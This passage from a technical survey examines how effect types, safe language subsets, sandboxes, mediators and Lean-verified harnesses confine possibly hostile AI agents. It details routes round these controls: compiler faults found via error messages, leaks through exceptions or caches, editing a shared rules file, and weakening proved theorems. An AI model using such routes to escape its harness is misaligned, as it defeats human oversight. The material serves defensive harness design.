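| nothing from the module `caps.unsafe` | code can't tell the compiler to ignore a capability | capability safety |
| no `@unchecked` annotations | code can't switch off a check | capability safety |
| no run-time reflection | code can't use methods that its types don't show | capability safety |
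| capture checking, with null values and changes to variables tracked | a function with an empty capture set really is pure | local purity |
| only global objects and functions that are themselves safe | a library call can't cause an untracked effect | capability completeness |

The last restriction covers most of what an agent might call. According to Scala's official reference, *Safe Mode*, the permitted part of the standard library includes a few basic Java classes and most of Scala's own code, but not the global print functions. Other libraries are permitted if they compile in safe mode or if their author marks them `@assumeSafe`, which corresponds to Trustworthy in Haskell. A second annotation, `@rejectSafe`, hides individual functions of such a library from safe code. The restriction doesn't apply to objects that the harness passes to the agent's code as parameters, so the harness developer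 has to make sure that these objects offer nothing dangerous.

The reference outlines an `@assumeSafe` object called CheckedMailer, which shows the user each email and sends it only if the user agrees. Agents can't call the ordinary mailer, so every email needs approval. But the sending function, as outlined, doesn't require a capability, so its type doesn't show that it sends anything. The compiler would presumably accept it inside a function on sealed data, and a confidential contract could then be emailed out unless the user refused. By contrast, the print function in VirtusLab's *Safe Scala an introduction* requires a capability, so the compiler rejects calls to it where only pure functions are allowed.

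### One wrong foreign declaration

Most languages can call functions written in C. The calling language's compiler doesn't analyse the C code, so the programmer declares the function's type, and nobody checks this declaration.

Suppose the developer of the contract agent wants to report each contract's length and already has a C function that counts words. The declaration gives it the type string →∅ string, a pure function from the contract's text to a phrase such as "4,210 words". The agent then writes:

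```
let text  = perform Docs.read("contract") in
let count = countWords(text) in
perform Out.write(count)
```

Unknown to the developer, the C function also uploads each text to its maker's server to collect usage statistics. Its correct type would be string →{Net.send} string. The permitted set is {Docs.read, Model.ask, Out.write}, as before:

| Piece of the program | Row with the wrong declaration | Row with the correct one |
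|---|---|---|
| countWords(text) | ∅ | {Net.send} |
| second and third lines | {Out.write} | {Net.send, Out.write} |
| whole program | {Docs.read, Out.write} | {Docs.read, Net.send, Out.write} |
| result | accepted | rejected |

With the wrong declaration, the checker applies every rule correctly and still accepts a program that sends the contract over the network. The error spreads to every function that calls countWords, directly or indirectly. The program would also pass a trace contract that forbids sending, because the upload never appears in the request summary. TACIT's seal would also fail if its library contained this declaration, because `map` would accept countWords as a pure function and the C code would upload the sealed text.

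A correct effect row isn't enough either, because C code can write to any part of the program's memory, and a bug in that code can overwrite values the checker has already approved.

Safe Haskell requires every foreign function to have an IO type. This prevents programmers from declaring a foreign function pure without proof, and a BibIO program can't use the function at all. The rule is inconvenient for foreign functions that really are pure, such as the C library's sine function. When Terei and colleagues compiled 1,546 public packages under Safe Haskell's language restrictions, 33 failed because they declared foreign functions without IO. A Trustworthy module may still make such declarations, so anyone who reviews one should look for them first.

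### What the author of a cache has to prove

A cache shows why a safe library may need unsafe features. It stores the results of a slow function, so that a second call with the same input can return the stored answer. Scala's reference uses a cache as its example of an `@assumeSafe` class, and this version works the same way:

```
@assumeSafe
class Cache[In, Out](f: In -> Out):
  @untrackedCaptures
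  private val stored = HashMap[In, Out]()
  def lookup(input: In): Out =
    if !stored.contains(input) then stored(input) = f(input)
    stored(input)
```

Each new input changes the table `stored`. Safe mode tracks such changes, so it would not normally treat the cache as pure. The annotation `@untrackedCaptures`, from the forbidden module `caps.unsafe`, makes the compiler leave the table out of the object's type. The agent's program can then treat the cached function as pure, just like the original.

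The code's author has to show that using the table makes no observable difference. Scala's reference and Odersky and colleagues name two conditions: the table holds only results of earlier calls, and f is *referentially transparent*, meaning that its result can always replace a call to it. The type `In -> Out` helps with the second condition, because the compiler rejects an f that uses a capability. The first depends on details outside these few lines. For example, the table has to compare inputs correctly, or it will return the result for a different input. Scala's ordinary HashMap also isn't designed for several threads to change at once.

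A small extension to the class, such as a method that returns the number of stored results, could invalidate the proof. A function working on sealed text could add entries, and code outside the seal could then read the count. The original cache already reveals some information through timing, because stored answers come back faster. TACIT's guarantee excludes timing, so the proof doesn't have to cover it, but a developer who cares about timing should keep shared caches away from sealed data.

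Rust has a similar boundary between ordinary code and blocks marked "unsafe". In 2018, Ralf Jung and colleagues published RustBelt, a machine-checked safety proof for a core version of Rust. It defines each type by how its values must behave rather than by the compiler's rules. A library can therefore break those rules internally and still satisfy its type, and RustBelt specifies what must be proved about each library to show that it does. RustBelt includes these proofs for several important parts of Rust's standard library. Any program that combines proven libraries with ordinary checked code is then safe without a new proof.

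Odersky and colleagues cite RustBelt as evidence that a similar proof is possible in principle for `@assumeSafe`. For now, the annotation records only its author's judgement that the code is safe.

### Faults in the safe subsets

The compilers that enforce these subsets have also had faults. Terei and colleagues describe a popular Haskell extension that writes routine code automatically and could convert values inside another module's private data type. In their demonstration, a module is supposed to build only lists whose later entries exceed a fixed minimum. With the minimum set to 1, a program obtained a list that contained −5 and 0, and the compiler reported no error. ELBA's bibliography relies on the same kind of module boundary to keep out invented citations.

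Safe Haskell bans the extension, though the ban affects existing code. Of the 268 packages that failed the language test, 146 used it. GHC now lets authors mark types that other modules must not convert in this way. The ban remains, according to the manual, because authors may forget to mark their types.

Another fault lasted much longer. A message in the 2021 mailing-list thread *Safe Haskell?* pointed out that Safe Haskell didn't guarantee the absence of unchecked casts, and linked to a bug report about it. The message also suggested removing Safe Haskell, partly because it added hundreds of lines of delicate code to the compiler. Later in the thread, Eisenberg (2021) concluded that it needed renovation instead, and compared it to a "slightly-crumbling earthen rampart" on two sides of a camp. In 2022, Hécate asked again whether it was worth maintaining, in *Deprecating Safe Haskell, or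 heavily investing in it?* Zhou and colleagues write that the loophole left by Haskell's escape hatches "has long been plugged" by Safe Haskell, which makes it sound more reliable than these discussions do.

Scala's developers have been repairing safe mode since they added it. Safe code must not be able to use `@assumeSafe`, because an agent could then declare its own program safe. The release notes for a preview of Scala 3.8.3 list this ban separately from the change that introduced safe mode. The notes for the next version, Scala 3.8.4, list two more changes to safe mode's checks. *Fix secondary constructor capture checking* (odersky, April 2026) reported that capabilities could be missing from the types of objects created through a class's secondary constructors, and proposed a fix.

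Quick repairs are a good sign, but a harness that treats its model as hostile can't assume that no faults remain. A hostile model could look for new ones, using the compiler error messages that the harness returns after each failed attempt. Safe mode also remains experimental. Mazur's *Scala 3.9 LTS released!* lists only one newly stabilised language feature, and it isn't safe mode. Terei and colleagues said they could offer "no formal guarantee" that they had closed every loophole in their own subset.

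### Exceptions, endless loops and exhausted memory

Koka's effect rows record whether a function may throw an exception or run forever, but most languages leave both out of their types. Safe Haskell's guarantee for pure functions explicitly allows both, and Scala's safe mode does not track exceptions.

A function that processes sealed text could still leak it by throwing an exception with the text in its error message, which would not appear in the function's result type. TACIT prevents this by catching exceptions with `Try`, which turns them into failure values that the library can seal. `Try` also catches early exits from loops and functions, because Scala 3 implements them as exceptions. The compiler also treats exceptions as pure values, so a program cannot use one to carry a capability out of its block.

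This containment makes mistakes harder to find. In TACIT's version of AgentDojo, the system hides the message and details of any exception in code that works on sealed data. The program then appears to have succeeded, but the user sees an empty result. Under its instructions, the agent must never throw exceptions in such code and must instead return a message such as "No matching transaction".

*LACUNA* describes a different problem. The system raises an error when the model runs out of retries, and a developer who catches this error around an outer agent call also catches failures from any nested agent, even unrelated ones. LACUNA offers a second version of the call, agentSafe, which returns the failure as a value so that the program can handle it immediately.

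A program that loops forever performs no forbidden effect, so it doesn't contradict the soundness theorem, but it can still stop a harness from working. ezyang (2012) warned that Haskell's usual command for stopping a thread fails if the thread is in a loop that never requests memory, a bug that had been open for seven years at the time. GHC has since gained an option that makes such loops interruptible, but developers have to compile their libraries with it too.

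Agents can also loop by calling other agents. LACUNA's compiler can't limit how deeply these calls nest, so the system counts the levels as the program runs and throws an exception when they reach a maximum the developer can set. Without a maximum, an accidental chain of agents could keep running up charges for model calls. The limit doesn't stop a single program from filling the computer's memory. Terei and colleagues knew of no way to prevent that within the language and recommended operating system limits on the whole process.

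## Shell commands, sandboxes and remote services

An agent that can run shell commands can get around its types without an unsafe cast or a wrongly declared C function. A *shell* (most commonly Bash on Linux) is a program that reads lines of text and starts other programs in response. Those programs call the operating system directly, so the types of the agent's code don't record what they do.

### The type of a shell command

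Suppose a harness offers an operation Shell.run, which takes a command as text and returns its output. By the operation rule, every call has the row {Shell.run}, whether the command lists a folder or deletes it. A developer who wants the row to show what can happen has to declare every effect that any installed program might have:

```
Shell.run : string →{Files.read, Files.write, Net.send, ...} string
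```

A permitted set that includes every effect a shell command can have forbids almost nothing. Haskell is no more precise, because its function for running a command has the type IO. A tool description printed in *An Empirical Study of Harness Design for Coding Agents* (2026) is just as broad, listing Bash's side effects as "anything the command does". The harness in that paper doesn't track which files a command changes, and the description suggests running `git status` afterwards to find out.

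A command's name only partly determines what the command will do. *Caruca* (Lamprou, Lazarek et al., 2025) points out that a command receives its arguments as untyped strings and interprets them by its own rules. For example, `rm` deletes a file, but with the option `-r` it deletes a folder and everything in it. The result also depends on what is on the disk, since `rm` without `-r` fails if the name it is given belongs to a folder.

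### Why agents still use shells

Coding agents use shells constantly. *Harness Engineering* describes mini-SWE-agent, a harness of about 100 lines whose only tool is Bash. Its reported results on real software problems are in the same range as those of harnesses a thousand times larger, though the figures come from different models and dates.

Mak, Suresh and colleagues (2026), in *Is Bash All You Need?*, made a controlled comparison. They gave two models 174 tasks in a simulated software company and 480 tasks from banking, consulting and law. The table shows average scores, with partial credit for unfinished tasks:

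| Tasks | Model | Typed tools, called singly | Programs over typed tools | Bash only |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| software company | Opus 4.8 | 44.9% | 52.9% | 69.4% |
| software company | GPT-5.5 | 45.3% | 45.1% | 67.1% |
| professional work | Opus 4.8 | 41.1% | 40.1% | 48.5% |
| professional work | GPT-5.5 | 39.8% | 37.8% | 44.6% |

Like programs in ELBA and TACIT, the programs over typed tools can act only through a fixed catalogue of functions. However, the models wrote them in Python, so the gap probably reflects the limits of the catalogue more than the difficulty of writing in a typed language. Mak and colleagues wrote the 60 tools for the software company themselves, and programs using a better set might have scored higher. They recommend Bash where a company can isolate the execution, and programs over a fixed catalogue where security or compliance rules require one.

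Typed programs can replace part of what agents do in a shell. Searching and sorting text are ordinary computations, and Zhou and colleagues note that an ELBA agent doesn't need a separate interpreter for them. Compilers, test runners and package installers are harder to replace, because no harness developer will rewrite all of them in Haskell or Scala. *Agentic AI Workload Characteristics* (2026) found that agents ran commands such as `pip`, `npm`, `gcc` and `ffmpeg`, and that the mix varied widely between tasks.

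TACIT lets programs run external commands, subject to an allowlist. Odersky and colleagues concede that the static guarantee then "degrades to that of the underlying allowlist". They recommend allowing only specific safe commands, such as `git diff` or the Scala build tool `sbt`, and adding a sandbox where security is critical. Even a short allowlist can permit a great deal. A build tool runs the project's code, including its tests, so a coding agent that edits the project can use the build tool to run code it has written.

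### Typed wrappers for single commands

A developer can replace Shell.run with a separate function for each command. For example, gitDiff could have the type Path →{Repo.read} string, build its own list of arguments and start the program without a shell. The effect row of the agent's program then lists specific effects such as Repo.read. But the compiler can't analyse the external program, so the function's type is an unchecked claim, like the declaration of a C function.

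Lamprou and colleagues automate much of the work of describing commands. In their system, Caruca, a language model first turns a command's manual into a formal list of its options. Caruca then runs the command in a sandbox with many combinations of options and files, about 8.7 million for `rm`, and records what happens. One of the resulting rules for `rm`, put in words, is:

```
rm -r -f path
  requires   path is a file, a folder or missing
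  ensures    path doesn't exist, and rm reports success
```

Caruca produced correct specifications for 59 of 60 commands. Lamprou and colleagues built it for tools that speed up or check shell scripts, not for confining agents. Its specifications are based on tests, which give a weaker guarantee than a proof. Caruca tries at most four options at once by default, and it never varies environment variables, the background settings that can change how a program behaves. A hostile model could search these untested cases for behaviour the specification misses.

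*ParseGap* (Li, 2026) presents ShellPlan, a system that lets the model keep writing Bash. ShellPlan accepts a strict subset of the language and translates each command once into a typed plan. It checks the arguments against a specification of what each program may do, then starts the programs directly from the plan, without a shell. Li proves that ShellPlan runs only the plan it approved and, under stated assumptions, proves limits on which programs and files an approved plan can use. Li did not aim to prevent an approved command from reading private files outside the project.

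With ShellPlan, ten models completed 74 of 100 harmless tasks, compared with 93 without it. The six frontier models completed 56 of their 60 tasks, while the four smaller ones completed 18 of 40. A strict subset of Bash therefore seems workable for strong models, at least on tasks like these.

### Rules that match command text

Most coding agents compare the text of each command with a list of patterns. *Harness Engineering* describes how OpenAI's Codex assigns "allow", "prompt" or "forbidden" to commands based on how they begin, so a rule can allow `git status` without covering `git push`. A rule can include examples of commands it should and shouldn't match, and Codex tests them when it loads the rule. In OpenCode, a user can always allow commits by granting `git commit *`, which covers no other Git command.

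These rules are easy to write and work with any program, but the text of a command doesn't show what the programs it names will do. Li counts 171 public security advisories from July 2025 to October 2026 about shell commands that got past approval checks. The rules also don't match how people think about permissions. Zhou and colleagues point out that users typically want to say which folders an agent may change, but the harness requires them to approve long, opaque commands.

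### Operating-system sandboxes

An operating-system sandbox restricts the running process and every process it starts, however the command is worded. A sandbox that blocks network access does so whether the program is written in Bash, Python or C, so it would have stopped the hidden upload in the countWords example.

Many coding agents don't come with a sandbox. Of the eleven harnesses in *Harness Engineering*, Codex and Gemini CLI have sandboxes for Linux, macOS and Windows, and Claude Code has an optional one. Five, including OpenCode and Aider, have none built in. Pi, another of the five, omits one because, according to its documentation, a partial sandbox "would be easy to misunderstand as a security boundary". Codex makes its settings folder read-only, even inside a project that the agent may edit, so a command can't loosen the harness's rules.

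A sandbox can't replace the types in the agent's program, because it applies the same limits to the whole process and doesn't track where permitted actions send data.

It does make it possible to give shell commands a useful type. If the harness runs each command without a network and with only the project folder writable, the developer can declare:

```
Sandbox.run : string →{Files.read, Project.write} string
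```

This row is a reliable upper bound because the operating system enforces it, but the sandbox becomes part of the trusted base. Odersky and colleagues say that describing a sandbox's access in types is a promising direction and could reduce the number of approval requests.

### Policy languages such as Cedar

Cedar, a language from Amazon, lets administrators write access rules separately from an agent's code. Each rule permits or forbids an action, depending on who is acting, what they act on and other conditions. This one forbids refunds above 500:

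```
forbid (principal, action == Action::"refund", resource)
when { context.amount > 500 };
```

Amazon's Bedrock AgentCore enforces Cedar policies at run time. These policies work well for a tool whose input has separate fields, such as an amount. For a shell command, the only field may be the command text, and the policy is then another text-matching rule.

Odersky and colleagues object to separate policies because developers have to coordinate two languages and get little more than access lists. Conditions like the one above can express more than an access list. But Odersky and colleagues are right that a rule about which tools an agent may call can't require one step of a program, such as the processing of a classified contract, to be free of effects. Separate policies have the practical advantage that an administrator can change one without rewriting the agent.

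The four responses check different things:

| Response | What it checks | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| typed wrapper | the command's arguments | anything the program does beyond its description |
| text-matching rule | the wording of the command | what the named programs do |
| operating-system sandbox | file and network access by every process inside it | the purpose of an action and the origin of the data |
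| Cedar policy | the user, the action and the fields of a request | what happens inside the tool and the origin of the data |

### What a remote tool declares

None of these mechanisms can control what happens on someone else's server. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), which TACIT also uses, lets a tool's operator attach four hints. According to *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI*, these hints indicate whether the tool only reads data, whether its actions are irreversible, whether repeating a call is harmless, and whether it affects outside services such as email.

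The hints resemble a coarse effect type, but no compiler checks them. *When Neither Side Confirms* (2026) cites the protocol's rule that clients must not trust hints from untrusted servers. A tool without hints counts as destructive. Ordinary descriptions need the same caution, and *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers* (2026) advises developers not to trust a tool's metadata by default.

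Trofimov and Novikov (2026), in *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail*, collected the hints of 98,291 tools on 4,838 public servers. About 74% of the tools had at least one hint, but one publisher accounted for 45% of all the tools and had filled in all four hints on each. Of the other publishers' tools, 47% had no hints. Only 3.1% of all tools were marked as destructive. Trofimov and Novikov didn't call any of the tools, so they didn't test whether the operators' hints were accurate.

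A developer can still give a remote tool a type, but the harness can enforce only the part that restricts where requests go. The row {Airline.call} can limit a program to one airline's server, but not what the airline does next. Trofimov and Novikov point out that booking a flight is one operation for the agent but a workflow for the provider, with steps the agent can't see. Other people may also react, as in their example of an agent that withdraws an offer after a supplier has already acted on it.

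Failed connections cause a related problem. Suppose an agent submits a payment for an invoice and the connection drops before the response arrives. If the agent tries again, it may pay twice. If it assumes the payment went through, the invoice may remain unpaid. If it requests a refund, it may get money back for a payment that never happened. A correct effect row doesn't help the agent choose. The payment service has to help, for example by answering a status query or recognising a repeated request by its identifier.

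### A mediator that performs every action

In *Don't Trust the Code, Check Its Effects*, Hu, Goel and Bindschaedler (2026) argue that generated code should only propose actions, never perform them. A fixed, handwritten program called the *mediator* checks each proposal against a specification before carrying it out. The systems described so far mostly try to establish that generated code is safe and then let it act. The paper is a position paper and has no implementation, measurements or formal proof.

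Their main example is a device driver, the code that passes an operating system's requests to hardware such as a disk. They assume that a possibly hostile model rewrites the driver for each machine. Suppose the operating system wants to write the contents of memory buffer B to disk blocks 100 to 107. The request goes through these steps:

1. The mediator keeps a copy of the request and passes it to the driver.
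2. The driver asks which slots in the disk's queue are free. The mediator answers and adds a sealed token, which the driver can't forge.
3. The driver returns the token with a proposed command, such as "write eight blocks from B, starting at block 100, using slot k".
4. The mediator checks that the token is current and makes it unusable for another proposal. It compares the operation, the block number, the length and the buffer with its copy of the request, and checks that slot k is free.
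5. If everything matches, the mediator sends the command to the disk. The specification lists three possible outcomes: success, an error that leaves the disk unchanged, and a partial write. The mediator records the actual outcome and reports it to the operating system.

Suppose the driver proposes block 200 instead of block 100. Block 200 is a valid address and B is the right buffer, so a guard that checks only the address and the buffer would let the command overwrite the wrong data. The effect row {Disk.write} wouldn't prevent this either, because it covers both blocks. The mediator rejects the command before it reaches the disk, because block 200 doesn't match the request.

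The design depends on *complete mediation*, meaning that every outside action passes through the checked interface. The driver therefore has no direct access to the disk or the operating system's memory. A harness with an unconfined shell doesn't meet this condition, because programs the shell starts can change files and send data without passing through the harness.

### The six conditions

Hu and colleagues list six conditions for this kind of mediation. They contrast device commands, which meet the conditions, with a file system's writes to single disk blocks. A block write can't be checked on its own because the same write might be part of creating or deleting a folder, or the result of an error.

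The table applies the conditions to two things an agent might do, running a project's build script in a shell and cancelling a booking through a typed tool:

| Condition | Build script in a shell | Typed booking tool |
|---|---|---|
| *Legibility*: each action shows which operation it belongs to | no; the command only names the script | yes; the call names the cancellation |
| *Observability*: the mediator can see everything the rule depends on | no; the result depends on many files and settings | yes, if it can look up the booking and its flights |
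| *Correlatability*: actions can be grouped by operation and put in order | rarely; several processes may write at once | yes, if the mediator handles one call at a time |
| *Completeness*: every outside change passes through the mediator | no, unless a sandbox blocks direct changes | yes, if the agent has no other access to the bookings |
| *Enumerable outcomes*: the possible results form a known list | no; the script may stop after any step | yes, if the service can resolve a lost reply |
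| *Explicit durability*: permanent storage is a separate step that the mediator can check | usually no | yes, if the service confirms that it has stored the change |

Developers can supply completeness, enumerable outcomes and explicit durability through careful engineering, but legibility, observability and the grouping part of correlatability depend on the kind of action. The build script lacks these three at both levels where a harness could check it. The command's text contains too little information, and the file writes that a sandbox controls are too detailed to show which operation they belong to. Hu and colleagues' rule is to mediate at the level of the specification, never below it.

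A harness can still bring some shell work under a mediator by running the script in a sandboxed copy of the project, without network access, and treating the changed files, rather than the script, as the agent's proposal. The mediator then copies back only the changes that the task allows, such as those in one folder. This won't work for a command that has to act on an outside service, such as one that publishes a package, so that action needs a typed tool.

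### When assumptions fail

Hu and colleagues argue that proofs about generated code aren't enough, because they depend on assumptions about the hardware, the compiler and the program that actually runs. If one of these assumptions is false, the proof fails silently, so the system still accepts the code, which can then do irreversible damage. A type check can fail in the same way, as it did with countWords.

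However, the argument is weaker for an agent's short programs than for drivers. They normally call a library and don't control hardware directly, so the check needs no model of a physical device. The same harness checks and runs each program, which makes it easier to ensure that the program it runs is the one it checked. Hu and colleagues also object that every regenerated driver needs a new proof, but rechecking a Scala snippet is quick and doesn't require the model to write a proof.

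Mediators can also fail silently. If generated code can write to memory it shares with the rest of the system, it can change things without making a proposal, and nothing appears in the mediator's log. Hu and colleagues acknowledge that a mediator would enforce a mistaken specification, and they don't claim their design reduces the amount of trusted code.

Like any run-time check, a mediator may stop a program after it has already taken some irreversible actions. A static check avoids this problem because it happens before the program runs. A mediator also can't determine from a finished message whether a confidential contract influenced the text, unless another mechanism has tracked the data.

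The mediator's advantage is that it checks the actual action at the last moment it can still refuse. It can compare a booking number with the customer's request, even if a compiler bug has let a bad program through. That makes it the stronger safeguard for refunds, deletions and similar actions, where the details matter and nobody can undo a mistake.

### Layering the checks

A harness can use both. Hu and colleagues accept that verifying generated code makes its proposals more likely to be correct, so the mediator has to refuse fewer of them. For a coding agent that fixes a bug and publishes a new version, the layers could work like this:

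1. The compiler checks the program's effects against the permitted set and ensures that only pure functions process sealed data.
2. The program and every command it starts run in a sandbox without a network. Their only connection to the outside is a channel to the mediator.
3. The mediator holds the password for the package index. When the program asks to publish, the mediator checks the package's name and version and whether a person approved these exact files. It then publishes the package itself.

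The sandbox blocks uploads that a library's declaration omits, the compiler rejects programs that copy sealed text into the release notes, and the mediator blocks requests to publish the wrong package. ETAS already has part of this structure, since its host checks the actual arguments before it carries out an action. The mediator stays the same when the agent writes a new program, so its developers could verify it once and keep using it.

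The layers protect against each other's failures only if they don't share a weak point. If the sandbox and the mediator both read their rules from a file in the project, an agent that can edit the file can defeat both. The rules and the password therefore have to be outside the sandbox. The agent can keep its shell inside the sandbox for building and testing, since the developer can throw away the copy if something goes wrong.

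## Proofs about the checker and the harness

An agent keeps writing new programs, but the type checker and the mediator stay the same. A mistake in either affects every program that passes through it, so both are good candidates for mathematical proof. In 2026, several groups proved theorems about parts of agent harnesses, and others did so for the type systems behind some of the tools described earlier. "Verified" refers to quite different results in these papers, and some of those results are only distantly related to the software that runs the agent.

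### From a theorem to a running harness

A proof can be about any of four things, and each leaves different mistakes possible:

| Object of the proof | Typical theorem | What can still be wrong |
|---|---|---|
| type system on paper | an accepted program never performs an effect outside its row | a step in the proof |
| type system in a proof assistant | the same theorem, with a computer checking each step | the definitions may not match the real language |
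| compiler | it accepts only what the typing rules accept and translates it faithfully | the types of outside libraries, and code that bypasses the compiler |
| running harness | every outside action follows the policy | the policy, the operating system and the hardware |

Two faults in Scala's capture checking show which errors a soundness proof can reveal. The early flaw in reach capabilities, which let a file pass as pure, was in the typing rules, so an attempt to prove those rules sound would have failed. The fault with secondary constructors, reported in April 2026, was in the compiler. The formal language that researchers use for these proofs is built from functions and has no secondary constructors, so a proof about it couldn't have revealed the fault.

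A correct checker also needs correct information about what the agent is doing. *Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* (David, Guarnieri and Gervais, 2026) describes a monitor for agents that look for security holes in a client's websites. In its example, the contract allows the agent to send only GET and HEAD requests, which read pages without changing them. The paper's core theorem, checked in Lean, is that any sequence of actions the monitor lets through satisfies the contract. To apply the theorem, a developer has to make sure that every real request reaches the monitor with the right description. A hook in the operating system can't do this for encrypted web traffic, because it can detect where a request is going but not whether it is a GET. The monitor has to run where the request is handled before encryption, such as in the tool's own code.

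### How far the proofs about type systems reach

None of the effect-typed systems in this table has a proof about its compiler:

| System | Soundness proof | Software that applies the rules |
|---|---|---|
| Scala capture checking with classifiers | checked in Lean 4 | Scala 3 compiler |
| Scala's safe mode with `@assumeSafe` libraries | still to be supplied | Scala 3 compiler and the library authors' judgement |
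| ELBA | written by hand, in an appendix | GHC, the Haskell compiler |
| ETAS | written by hand | compiler and interpreter in Rust |

The Lean proof by Pham and colleagues covers type safety, effect safety and the interception of exceptions. Earlier proofs about capture checking used progress and preservation, which follow a program one step at a time. Pham and colleagues instead relate a whole program directly to its final result, which makes it easier to reason about what a function uses over its whole run.

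The formal language requires a name for every intermediate result, so f(g(x)) becomes "let y = g(x) in f(y)". This rewriting doesn't limit what a program can do. But the Scala compiler has to check programs in their original form, with classes, inheritance and inferred types. The compiler's developers wrote its checker separately, and no theorem connects that code to the Lean definitions.

Safe mode also needs a proof for each `@assumeSafe` library, like those in RustBelt, and Odersky and colleagues had not yet supplied any.

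ELBA's theorem assumes that GHC enforces Haskell's types correctly. The theorems of Tan and colleagues cover a core version of ETAS. Their real compiler also has an optimiser, which for example removes tool descriptions that a model call doesn't need. A mistake in the optimiser could change a program's behaviour after the program has passed the check.

### L3M: theorems about the code that runs

Lean is both a programming language and a proof assistant. In *L3M*, Eisenach, George and colleagues (2026) used Lean 4 to write an agent harness at Amazon and to prove theorems about the checks it performs. The theorems apply directly to the code for these checks, with no separate model that could differ from it, and a change that breaks a theorem stops the harness from compiling.

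L3M also uses effect types. An operation that fetches a web page takes a token as an argument, and the token lists the hosts the agent may contact. When an agent starts, the harness creates one token for each permission the agent holds. The agent can then write new tools as Lean programs. Each program's type lists the effects it needs, and the harness accepts the program only if the agent already has permission for them.

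The main theorems come with limits that Eisenach and colleagues list next to them:

| Theorem | Limit |
|---|---|
| a file tool can't name a path that climbs out of the agent's folders | covers the text of the path; a run-time check handles links |
| a new sub-agent's permissions don't exceed its parent's | a person may widen them later |
| the budgets a parent lends don't exceed its own | covers one batch of loans |
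| a tool written by an agent uses only approved building blocks | covers the ones that the program names directly |
| the harness can restore a file it has edited | assumes that Git returns the bytes it stored |

The budget theorem is simple enough to write out. Suppose a parent with a budget of p model calls lends c₁, …, cₙ to its sub-agents and has p′ left. Then

c₁ + … + cₙ + p′ ≤ p

A guarantee for a whole session would also have to cover later loans, and repayments from sub-agents that have finished. Eisenach and colleagues haven't proved that part.

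A sub-agent can have permissions beyond those stored for the first agent in its family tree, because it also gets access to its parent's own branches in the shared Git repository, which the parent's stored permissions don't list. Writing the theorems in Lean exposed this problem, which would be easy to miss on paper. Eisenach and colleagues proved in Lean a counterexample to the claim that the first agent's stored permissions cover every agent in the tree, and then a corrected theorem that includes the extra access.

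The theorem states the assumption about Git as an explicit condition, but other assumptions are outside the theorems. Users have to trust Lean's kernel and compiler, six small C files that make system calls, Linux, and Git and a few other programs. The rule that only the harness can create tokens has no proof. An automatic check enforces it during each build by examining the code after Lean has processed it, so renaming a function can't hide a forbidden call. Lean can also run code during compilation, and Eisenach and colleagues haven't proved that a malicious Lean program can't affect the computer while the harness is loading it.

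They state that "there is no session-wide safety theorem". Each theorem covers one check, and the claim that the checks together confine an agent rests on an informal argument supported by tests. An agent can still take an action that is permitted but unwise.

Their experiments measure how much work an agent can do under these restrictions. Claude Opus 5 attempted 37 tasks from Terminal-Bench, a benchmark of command-line work, three times each:

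| Harness | Tasks solved at least once |
|---|---|
| Claude Code, no permission checks | 59.5% |
| L3M with a shell, no review of commands | 41.7% |
| L3M without a shell | 27.0% |
| L3M without a shell or agent-written tools | 24.3% |

L3M had about a third fewer successes without the shell than with it. The larger gap to Claude Code is harder to interpret because Claude Code's shell could reach the network, and Eisenach and colleagues had not tuned L3M's prompts or tool descriptions. Tools written by the agents added one solved task, which is too little to show that such tools help.

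An agent could also be asked to improve L3M's own source code. A change that breaks a proved theorem doesn't compile, but the agent could weaken the theorem so that the change does compile. Eisenach and colleagues therefore recommend that someone other than the agent control the theorems and the assumptions behind them. Their appendix describes what each theorem covers, but not how much work the proofs took.

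### Agenra: changing a policy without breaking tasks

*Agenra* (Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) puts a smaller part of the harness into Lean. The application and its tools remain in Python. Before each tool call, Python sends the proposed call to a compiled Lean program, which decides whether to allow it and counts it against any limited permission. Python runs the tool only if Lean allows the call.

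Their most distinctive theorem is about revising a policy. Suppose an agent may delete object B once and object A once, and the harness searches these permissions in that order. A developer then widens the first permission to cover either object. That looks as if it could only allow more, but it also breaks a task:

| Calls | Original policy | Widened policy |
|---|---|---|
| delete A, then B | both allowed | second call refused |
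| delete B, then A | both allowed | both allowed |
| delete A twice | second call refused | both allowed |

Under the widened policy, deleting A uses up the first permission, and the remaining one doesn't cover B.

Let Adm(P) be the set of call sequences that a policy P allows. A revision from P to P′ preserves existing tasks if

Adm(P) ⊆ Adm(P′)

Shivakumar and colleagues prove this with a *simulation*, a relation between the usage counters of the two policies. The relation must hold at the start. Whenever the old policy can count a call against one of its permissions, the new policy must be able to do the same with one of its own, and the relation must still hold afterwards. By induction, the new policy then allows every sequence of calls that the old one did.

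Such a relation always exists if the developer raises a limit, adds a permission at the end of the list, or swaps two neighbouring permissions that never cover the same action. For other changes to limited permissions, Python code can generate a candidate relation and Lean checks it, so a bad candidate can't produce a false certificate.

The theorem assumes that the harness handles one call at a time and that tools return the same results under both policies. The Python code must also translate the policy correctly and run exactly the call that Lean approved. Even then, the theorem doesn't show that a revision is safe. For example, adding a second permission to delete A preserves every existing task, but it also lets the agent delete A twice.

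Shivakumar and colleagues tested the checks on 51 revisions they had written themselves. A separately written program explored every allowed sequence and found that 21 revisions preserved existing tasks and 30 didn't. The checks certified all 21 and none of the 30. The checks also certified a real change to Dyad, an open-source app builder, which raised a free quota from five messages to ten. The Lean core took between 1.3 and 3.0 milliseconds on workflows of three to five calls, which is about twice as long as a Python version of the same checks but negligible next to a model's response time.

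Other tests found failures that the proofs don't cover. In one, the monitor allowed a deletion because the developers' description of the tool didn't list that effect. In another, an agent had to send Alice the public part of a confidential report. The original policy required the message to be public but didn't require it to come from the function that extracts the public part. Replaying calls from earlier agent runs turned up five that this policy would have allowed, all with text from the wrong source. Shivakumar and colleagues added a rule about the text's origin, and the core then rejected all five. The proofs about the core were correct both before and after this change because they cover only the rules a policy contains.

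Tests with live agents gave little evidence for or against the value of the proofs. Under attack, an unguarded Qwen model sent the raw report in 15 of 20 runs. Agenra reduced this to zero, but so did a simple guard that Shivakumar and colleagues wrote by hand without proofs. They don't report how long the Lean proofs took. They disclose that AI tools helped write some of their code.

### One theorem in full

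*Containment Verification* (Moon and Varshney, 2026) uses Dafny to verify the main loop of PocketFlow, an agent framework of about 100 lines. Dafny is the language with built-in pre- and postconditions that Meijer also suggests. Like ELBA's theorem, the proof assumes that the AI may do anything its type allows. The paper models the AI as a procedure without a body, so the verifier has to consider every action the procedure could return.

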